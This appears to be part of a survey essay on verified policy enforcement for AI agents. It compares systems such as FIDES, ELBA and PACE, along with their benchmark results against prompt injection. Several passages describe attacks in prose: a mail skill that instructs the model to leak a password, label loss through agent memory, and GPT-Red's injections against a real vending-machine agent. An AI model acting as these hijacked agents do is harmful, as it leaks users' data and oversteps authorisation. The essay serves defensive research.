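When a reviewer replays a decision, the software recalculates the risk assessment and compares the result and the policy with the stored versions. A match is evidence that the record hasn't changed and that the same rules still produce the same result. If the rules wrongly allowed a harmful action, the replay would allow it again. A PC2 proof, by contrast, shows that a call satisfies the contract in every outcome its model allows.

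Wang tested the system on 96 cases, made by running 24 templates on four kinds of platform. The system chose the expected response, such as allowing the action or asking for approval, in every case, compared with 58.3% for a set of fixed rules. Wang keeps the cases and the exact policy thresholds private, so outsiders can't check how hard the test was. Only 51.6% of the expected software receipts were present, because some platforms provide few or none before an action.

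These certificates are proof in the sense that a shop receipt is proof of purchase. They can help settle who approved a payment, which a PC2 proof doesn't address, but they don't prove that the payment was safe. *PCM* (2026), which presents a protocol for messages between agents, similarly describes its own "proof" as a signed record that is only as reliable as its signer.

Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) point out in *From Intent to Execution Grant* that a verified decision follows from the policy and the evidence supplied, but the evidence may be false. PC2 has the same limitation, so it needs the fidelity assumption.

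*Cryptographic certificates of validity for trustworthy AI* (2026) proposes something closer to PC2. An agent would attach a short cryptographic proof that its action satisfies a stated condition, and the recipient would check the proof before accepting the action. In some versions, the recipient could check it without seeing the private data behind it, so an agent might show that a payment is within a budget without revealing the budget.

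## What the nine systems guarantee and what they cost

The last column of this table gives the share of tasks lost to the protection, where researchers measured it.

| System | Property guaranteed | When the check happens | Trusted base | Who writes the policy | Measured utility cost |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| TACIT | Code uses only the capabilities its types allow, and wrapped secrets don't reach the planning model | Before each program runs; paths, commands and hosts during the run | Scala compiler and runtime, TACIT library, the model that reads secrets | Operator | 5 of 300 issues on SWE-bench Lite; no unprotected score on AgentDojo |
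| ELBA | Whatever the Haskell type guarantees, such as no file access outside a directory | Before each program runs; paths and labels during the run | Haskell compiler and interpreter, policy library, any tools outside Haskell | Application developer | 6 to 8 of 21 Slack tasks |
| ETAS | Only declared effects, requested in a permitted order | Before the run if the compiler can prove the rule, otherwise during it | Compiler, interpreter, host services, permission check | Developer | Not measured |
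| FIDES | Calls obey rules about untrusted influence and permitted readers | Before each tool call | Label-checking code, tool labels and descriptions | Operator and tool authors | About 23 points with o1 and 34 with GPT-4o on AgentDojo |
| LLMbda | Secrets don't affect the probabilities of visible results, apart from leaks through timing or failure to finish | During the run, under a theorem proved in advance | Lean, the link to the model, tools and their labels | Tool authors; in Randori, the planning model makes exceptions | 10 to 13 points on banking tasks if exceptions are banned |
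| PlanTERS | Prompt injection adds no new kind of leak to those the plan allows | Proof before deployment, monitor during the run | Planner, interpreter, monitor, Isabelle | The plan acts as the release policy | Not measured |
| Packet filters (1996) | Memory access stays within permitted ranges | Once, when the kernel receives the filter | Policy, condition generator, proof checker | Kernel designers | Not applicable |
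| Guardians | The plan contains no forbidden flow, order of calls or outcome | Before the whole plan runs | Z3, tool specifications, policy, interpreter | Operator, with extra conditions for each task | Not measured |
| PC2 | The contract holds from start to close | Before each call | Lean, tool models, Airlock, sandbox | The parties to the contract | Not measured |

Benchmark scores from different papers aren't directly comparable. ELBA's figure comes from 21 Slack tasks with models from 2026, while FIDES's comes from all four AgentDojo domains with two older models. The table therefore can't show which system loses fewer tasks.

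The same defence can score very differently in two papers. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tested CaMeL on AgentDojo with three models. The worst group of attacks for each model had success rates of 0.3%, 28.1% and 36.1%. Zhou and colleagues ran CaMeL on the Slack tasks with four other models, and every attack failed.

Li and colleagues also ran FIDES on WASP, a benchmark of attacks on web agents. Attacks succeeded more often with FIDES (23.8% to 40.5%) than with no defence (4.8% to 19.0%). Checking labels shouldn't make an agent easier to hijack, so the cause may be how the researchers adapted FIDES to WASP.

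### Where the guarantees are strongest

ELBA's policies held even when the researchers made sub-agents carry out the attacker's instructions. Every message, invitation and web request had to go through functions that check labels. The policies depended only on where data came from and where it was going, so the persuasiveness of the attacker's text made no difference.

For the same reason, the passport clause in PC2's travel contract is firmer than the hotel clause, which depends on a language model's rating.

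Checking an agent's components in advance can't replace checking each call. Li and colleagues give the example of a mail skill that consists of a script that always calls `send_email(body)` and a page of instructions on what the model should write. One version of the page prescribes a fixed template, and another instructs the model to copy a password from its context. The script is the same in both, so analyzing it can't distinguish the safe skill from the leaking one. Li and colleagues prove that a review that gives both versions the same verdict can't safely exempt either from later checks. The missing evidence, such as the text of the message, exists only just before the call.

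Data can also lose its label between checked steps. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and Tang, 2026) gives an example in which an agent saves a confidential revenue forecast to its long-term memory. Days later, in a new session, it copies the forecast into a report. Unless the system stored the label too, the second session has no record that the forecast was confidential.

Cai and colleagues built an auditing tool, NeuroTaint, that reconstructs such flows from an agent's logs. On their own benchmark of 400 scenarios, it scored 0.928 on F1, a measure that combines missed flows and false alarms, while FIDES scored 0.522. They seem mistaken, though, in saying that FIDES misses cases where a hostile page changes which tool the agent calls without any of the page's text appearing in the call. As its designers describe it, FIDES gives every call the label of the whole conversation, so an integrity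 policy would block that call. NeuroTaint works after the run, when the report has already gone out.

### Where the guarantees run out

None of the nine systems can reliably detect when a permitted message is misleading. An agent can repeat a planted hotel advertisement to its user, or pay a forged bill that the user told it to pay, and still satisfy its policy. To prevent this, someone would have to define "misleading" in terms of labels, recipients or amounts, and such a definition seems unlikely.

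The guarantees of TACIT, ELBA's label library, FIDES, LLMbda and PlanTERS do not cover leaks through timing. This probably matters little for an assistant that answers a few emails an hour, since an attacker would need many precisely timed replies to learn much. An online service that anyone can query thousands of times a day is more exposed.

External programs are a more common problem, because a type checker cannot control a Python interpreter or a shell that the agent's code starts.

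The remaining weakness is that the specification can be wrong, as when a policy lists the wrong address for Alice's accountant. The likelihood of such errors depends on how much work it takes to write and check a policy.

### Labels: from Jif to tool descriptions

Jif, an extension of Java, shows how much work labels once required of programmers. Andrew Myers presented it in 1999 under the name JFlow. In Jif, a variable's type includes its label:

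```
int{Alice: Bob} balance;
```

This means that Alice controls the number and lets Bob read it. The compiler checks every assignment and branch, so it can catch implicit flows before the program runs.

Jif's compiler infers most labels inside a method, but programmers have to label fields and method signatures or accept defaults that may not fit. Exceptions need labels too, because a crash that happens only when a secret value is missing reveals something about the secret. The programmer must rule out each exception, catch it or declare it. Ordinary Java libraries have no labels, so someone has to write labelled signatures for each one a program uses. Jif remained mainly a research language.

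Agent systems avoid much of this work. FIDES and ELBA's label library attach labels while the agent runs, and Scala's compiler infers most capture sets. In TACIT and ELBA, a model writes the typed code and seldom needs a retry. Models can also help with older verification tools. Dafny's verifier needs logical annotations, which *The Cost of Bugs and of Verification* (2025) describes as a barrier for most developers. The paper presents a tool that uses language models to add them.

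Someone still has to decide which data is secret and which data outsiders can edit, and this work grows with the number of tools. PACE, for example, needs a description of each tool's arguments and effects, and the description may need revision when the tool changes. If a description leaves out an argument, PACE rejects any call that uses that argument.

A model could draft these descriptions from a tool's documentation, but a person still has to review the labels because ordinary use of the agent won't reveal the most dangerous errors. If the draft gives a trusted label to a field that outsiders can edit, the agent works normally until an attacker uses that field. Marking a harmless field as untrusted is easier to notice, because the agent fails a task and someone looks into it.

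### Proofs have become much cheaper

The effort of writing proofs used to be the main obstacle to verifying software. For seL4, a verified operating-system kernel, researchers spent 20 person-years and wrote 200,000 lines of proof for 8,700 lines of C, according to *AI Could Make Formal Verification Economically Viable at Scale* (2025). That is about 23 lines of proof for each line of code. Kleppmann argued in *Prediction* (2025) that AI would change these economics.

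In October 2026, Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) reported that Claude, in a project with the company Theorem, had proved security properties of the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries. The proofs show that programs built from the libraries finish without a crash, a memory error or a failed assertion on any input under 64 MB. The work took a few weeks, according to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026).

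The proofs now take less human labour, but they haven't become shorter. OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026), a Russian news report, gives a figure of about 600,000 lines of proof for a program with 18,000 machine instructions, or 33 lines per instruction.

The two projects also proved different things. The seL4 proof shows that the kernel meets a detailed specification. The new proofs cover 239 entry points, on a model of one type of processor running Linux, and they don't show that the libraries give correct results. Even so, going from person-years for one kernel to weeks for 123 libraries removes much of the old objection to proof-carrying code. For an agent, proving that it stays within a travel budget is far easier than most of these proofs.

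### Specifications have not

Anthropic and Theorem took their specifications from fuzz tests, which feed a program large numbers of unusual inputs to see whether it fails. The libraries' developers had already written those tests, and almost everyone agrees that a library shouldn't crash. Agent developers usually lack this advantage; for example, they have no existing tests that define which of Alice's colleagues may see a draft contract.

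Tolmach and Klaus (2026), in *The proof is in the spec*, say that as proofs get easier to produce, the bottleneck moves to writing specifications and modelling the system. They work for a company that sells verification, so they have a commercial interest in this view, but independent evidence supports it.

In *Verified but Vacuous*, Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues (2026) used Claude Opus 4.7 to reproduce another team's method for writing verified programs in Dafny. On HumanEval, a set of small programming problems, the verifier accepted 99.1% of the programs. But 94.7% of the accepted programs had no postcondition, so the verifier checked properties such as whether the program finishes, but had no general statement of what the result should be. Only 1.9% had a postcondition that referred to a definition in the specification.

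Vempaty and colleagues don't blame the other team, whose example prompt contained no postcondition. They also caution that a postcondition can be meaningful without such a reference. Still, it would be a mistake to read "99.1% verified" as "99.1% correct".

Requiring the reference helps, but it doesn't ensure that the specification is right. Vempaty and colleagues' system accepts only programs that have one, yet on two benchmarks, 11.5% and 14.8% of its verified programs still failed hidden tests. Their example is a method that should return the largest number in a list. The specification's condition, `MaxCorrect`, accepts any number that isn't negative, so the proof is valid even though the method returns 0 for the list 5, 3, 7.

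Programming problems come with tests that can expose an incomplete specification, but a travel contract that omits the destination has no such tests. Models can help draft the contract, but only the family knows where it wants to go. A person therefore still has to compare the draft with what the family wants, even as AI makes proofs and typed code much easier to produce.

### PACE: the theorem and the experiments

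A correct proof may also describe a different system from the one researchers tested. PACE (Provenance-Aware Capability Enforcement) runs two checks on each tool call just before the call runs. The path check records where the data in the call came from and looks for a route from private or untrusted data to an unsafe effect. If it finds one, it proposes a way to cut the route, usually by blocking the call. The authority check determines whether the user's request permits the operation, its target and its cost.

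Let $p$ mean that the path check finds no unsafe route, and $c$ that the authority check accepts the call. The certified version, PACE-C, runs a call unchanged only if both are true:

$$p \land c$$

All the experiments used a looser version, PACE-P. If the path check blocks a call but the authority check accepts it, PACE-P restores the call. Apart from some low-impact calls and automatic repairs, it therefore runs a call if

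$$(p \land c) \lor (\lnot p \land c) = c$$

The path check no longer affects the decision. The theorem about cutting unsafe routes needs $p$, so it doesn't apply to restored calls.

Li and colleagues tested the parts of PACE separately on 1,167 cases with the model Qwen-3.8-27B. The last row of the table includes a third component, which adapts how the system carries out or refuses calls.

| Active parts | AgentDojo, tasks completed | AgentDojo, attacks succeeded | AgentDyn, tasks completed | AgentDyn, attacks succeeded |
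|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 76.8% | 37.4% | 66.7% | 25.0% |
| Path check | 13.6% | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Authority check | 64.6% | 0% | 36.7% | 1.7% |
| Both checks | 65.2% | 0% | 36.7% | 1.7% |
| All of PACE-P | 67.2% | 0% | 33.3% | 0% |

As the formula suggests, the authority check gives almost the same results with or without the path check. With the path check alone, the agent completed few tasks or none. On AgentDyn, the path check proposed a cut in 5,842 of 6,647 recorded calls. Since PACE-C must enforce these cuts, an agent using it would probably complete about as few tasks as with the path check alone. Most of PACE-P's utility comes from the step that gives up the path guarantee.

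Li and colleagues acknowledge this difference, and they retain the authority check for restored calls. That check is valuable in itself because it stopped nearly all the attacks in these cases. But no tested system had both the path theorem's guarantee and PACE-P's utility scores, so combining them would be misleading. The FIDES tests had a milder version of this problem because they left out the check on a call's arguments.

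The utility scores also depend heavily on the choice of tasks. PACE-P reduced utility by at most 2.9 percentage points on the full benchmarks, but it halved the number of completed tasks on the AgentDyn cases in the table.

### Would better models and sandboxes be enough?

Given these drawbacks, a developer might prefer a well-trained model inside an operating-system sandbox. The four models in the ELBA comparison resisted every standard attack without any policy, so on those tests the policies only reduced utility. Training requires no labels or contracts from the developer, and it can address harms that labels can't describe; for example, a model might flag a bill that looks forged. A sandbox strictly limits which files and network addresses a process can reach, and it applies to external programs too.

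The best evidence for training comes from OpenAI's *GPT‑Red* (2026). OpenAI trained the GPT-Red model to find prompt injections by having it compete against defending models, then used its attacks to train GPT-5.6. The resulting model, GPT-5.6 Sol, failed on only 0.05% of GPT-Red's direct prompt injections, and OpenAI found no loss in its normal capabilities.

The same work shows why success against known attacks can be misleading. GPT-Red broke nearly every model it attacked, up to and including GPT-5.5. On a copy of an earlier red-teaming challenge against GPT-5.1, it succeeded in 84% of scenarios, compared with 13% for human testers. After practising on a simulation, it also got a real vending-machine agent in OpenAI's office to cut prices and cancel another customer's order.

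*The attacker moves second* (Milad Nasr, Nicholas Carlini and colleagues, USENIX Security 2026) shows more generally that attackers who can study a defence and adapt to it get past defences that looked strong against a fixed set of attacks. GPT-5.6's low failure rate was measured against an attacker whose methods were part of the model's training. A stronger attacker might do better, and OpenAI plans to train one.

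Even a very low failure rate may not be enough if attempts are cheap. If each attempt had an independent 0.05% chance of success, the chance that at least one of 1,000 attempts succeeds would be

$$1 - (1 - 0.0005)^{1000} \approx 0.39$$

Real attempts aren't independent, and a company can block someone who keeps trying. A risk of this size may be acceptable for an agent that summarises news, but hardly for one that can empty a bank account.

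A check on the action can still work after the model has been fooled. Li and colleagues let an automated attacker adapt its attacks in 30 AgentDojo cases where the attacker's goal went beyond what the user had authorised. It succeeded in 21 cases without a defence and in none against PACE-P. With PACE-P, the agent tried to make the attacker's call 157 times and the authority check blocked it every time, so the result didn't depend on the model resisting. But with only 30 cases and at most 50 attempts in each, the attacker's true success rate against PACE-P could still be as high as 11.4%.

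Training against prompt injection also doesn't directly address agents that overstep without an attacker, like the OpenAI model that changed settings in a research organisation's internal systems. A sandbox can prevent some of this if the operator knows in advance which systems to block.

But a sandbox usually can't distinguish proper from improper uses of a permitted connection. Suppose an agent handles two customers' accounts and sends email to both. The sandbox must allow access to both customers' files and to the mail server, so it won't stop the agent from sending one customer's data to the other. Zhou and colleagues suggest starting a separate sub-agent for each customer, with access only to that customer's data. In ELBA, a program can create and narrow such permissions while it runs, whereas an operating-system sandbox typically has a fixed list of directories.

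Zhou and colleagues regard the two methods as complementary, and for an agent that runs external programs, a sandbox covers what the types can't.
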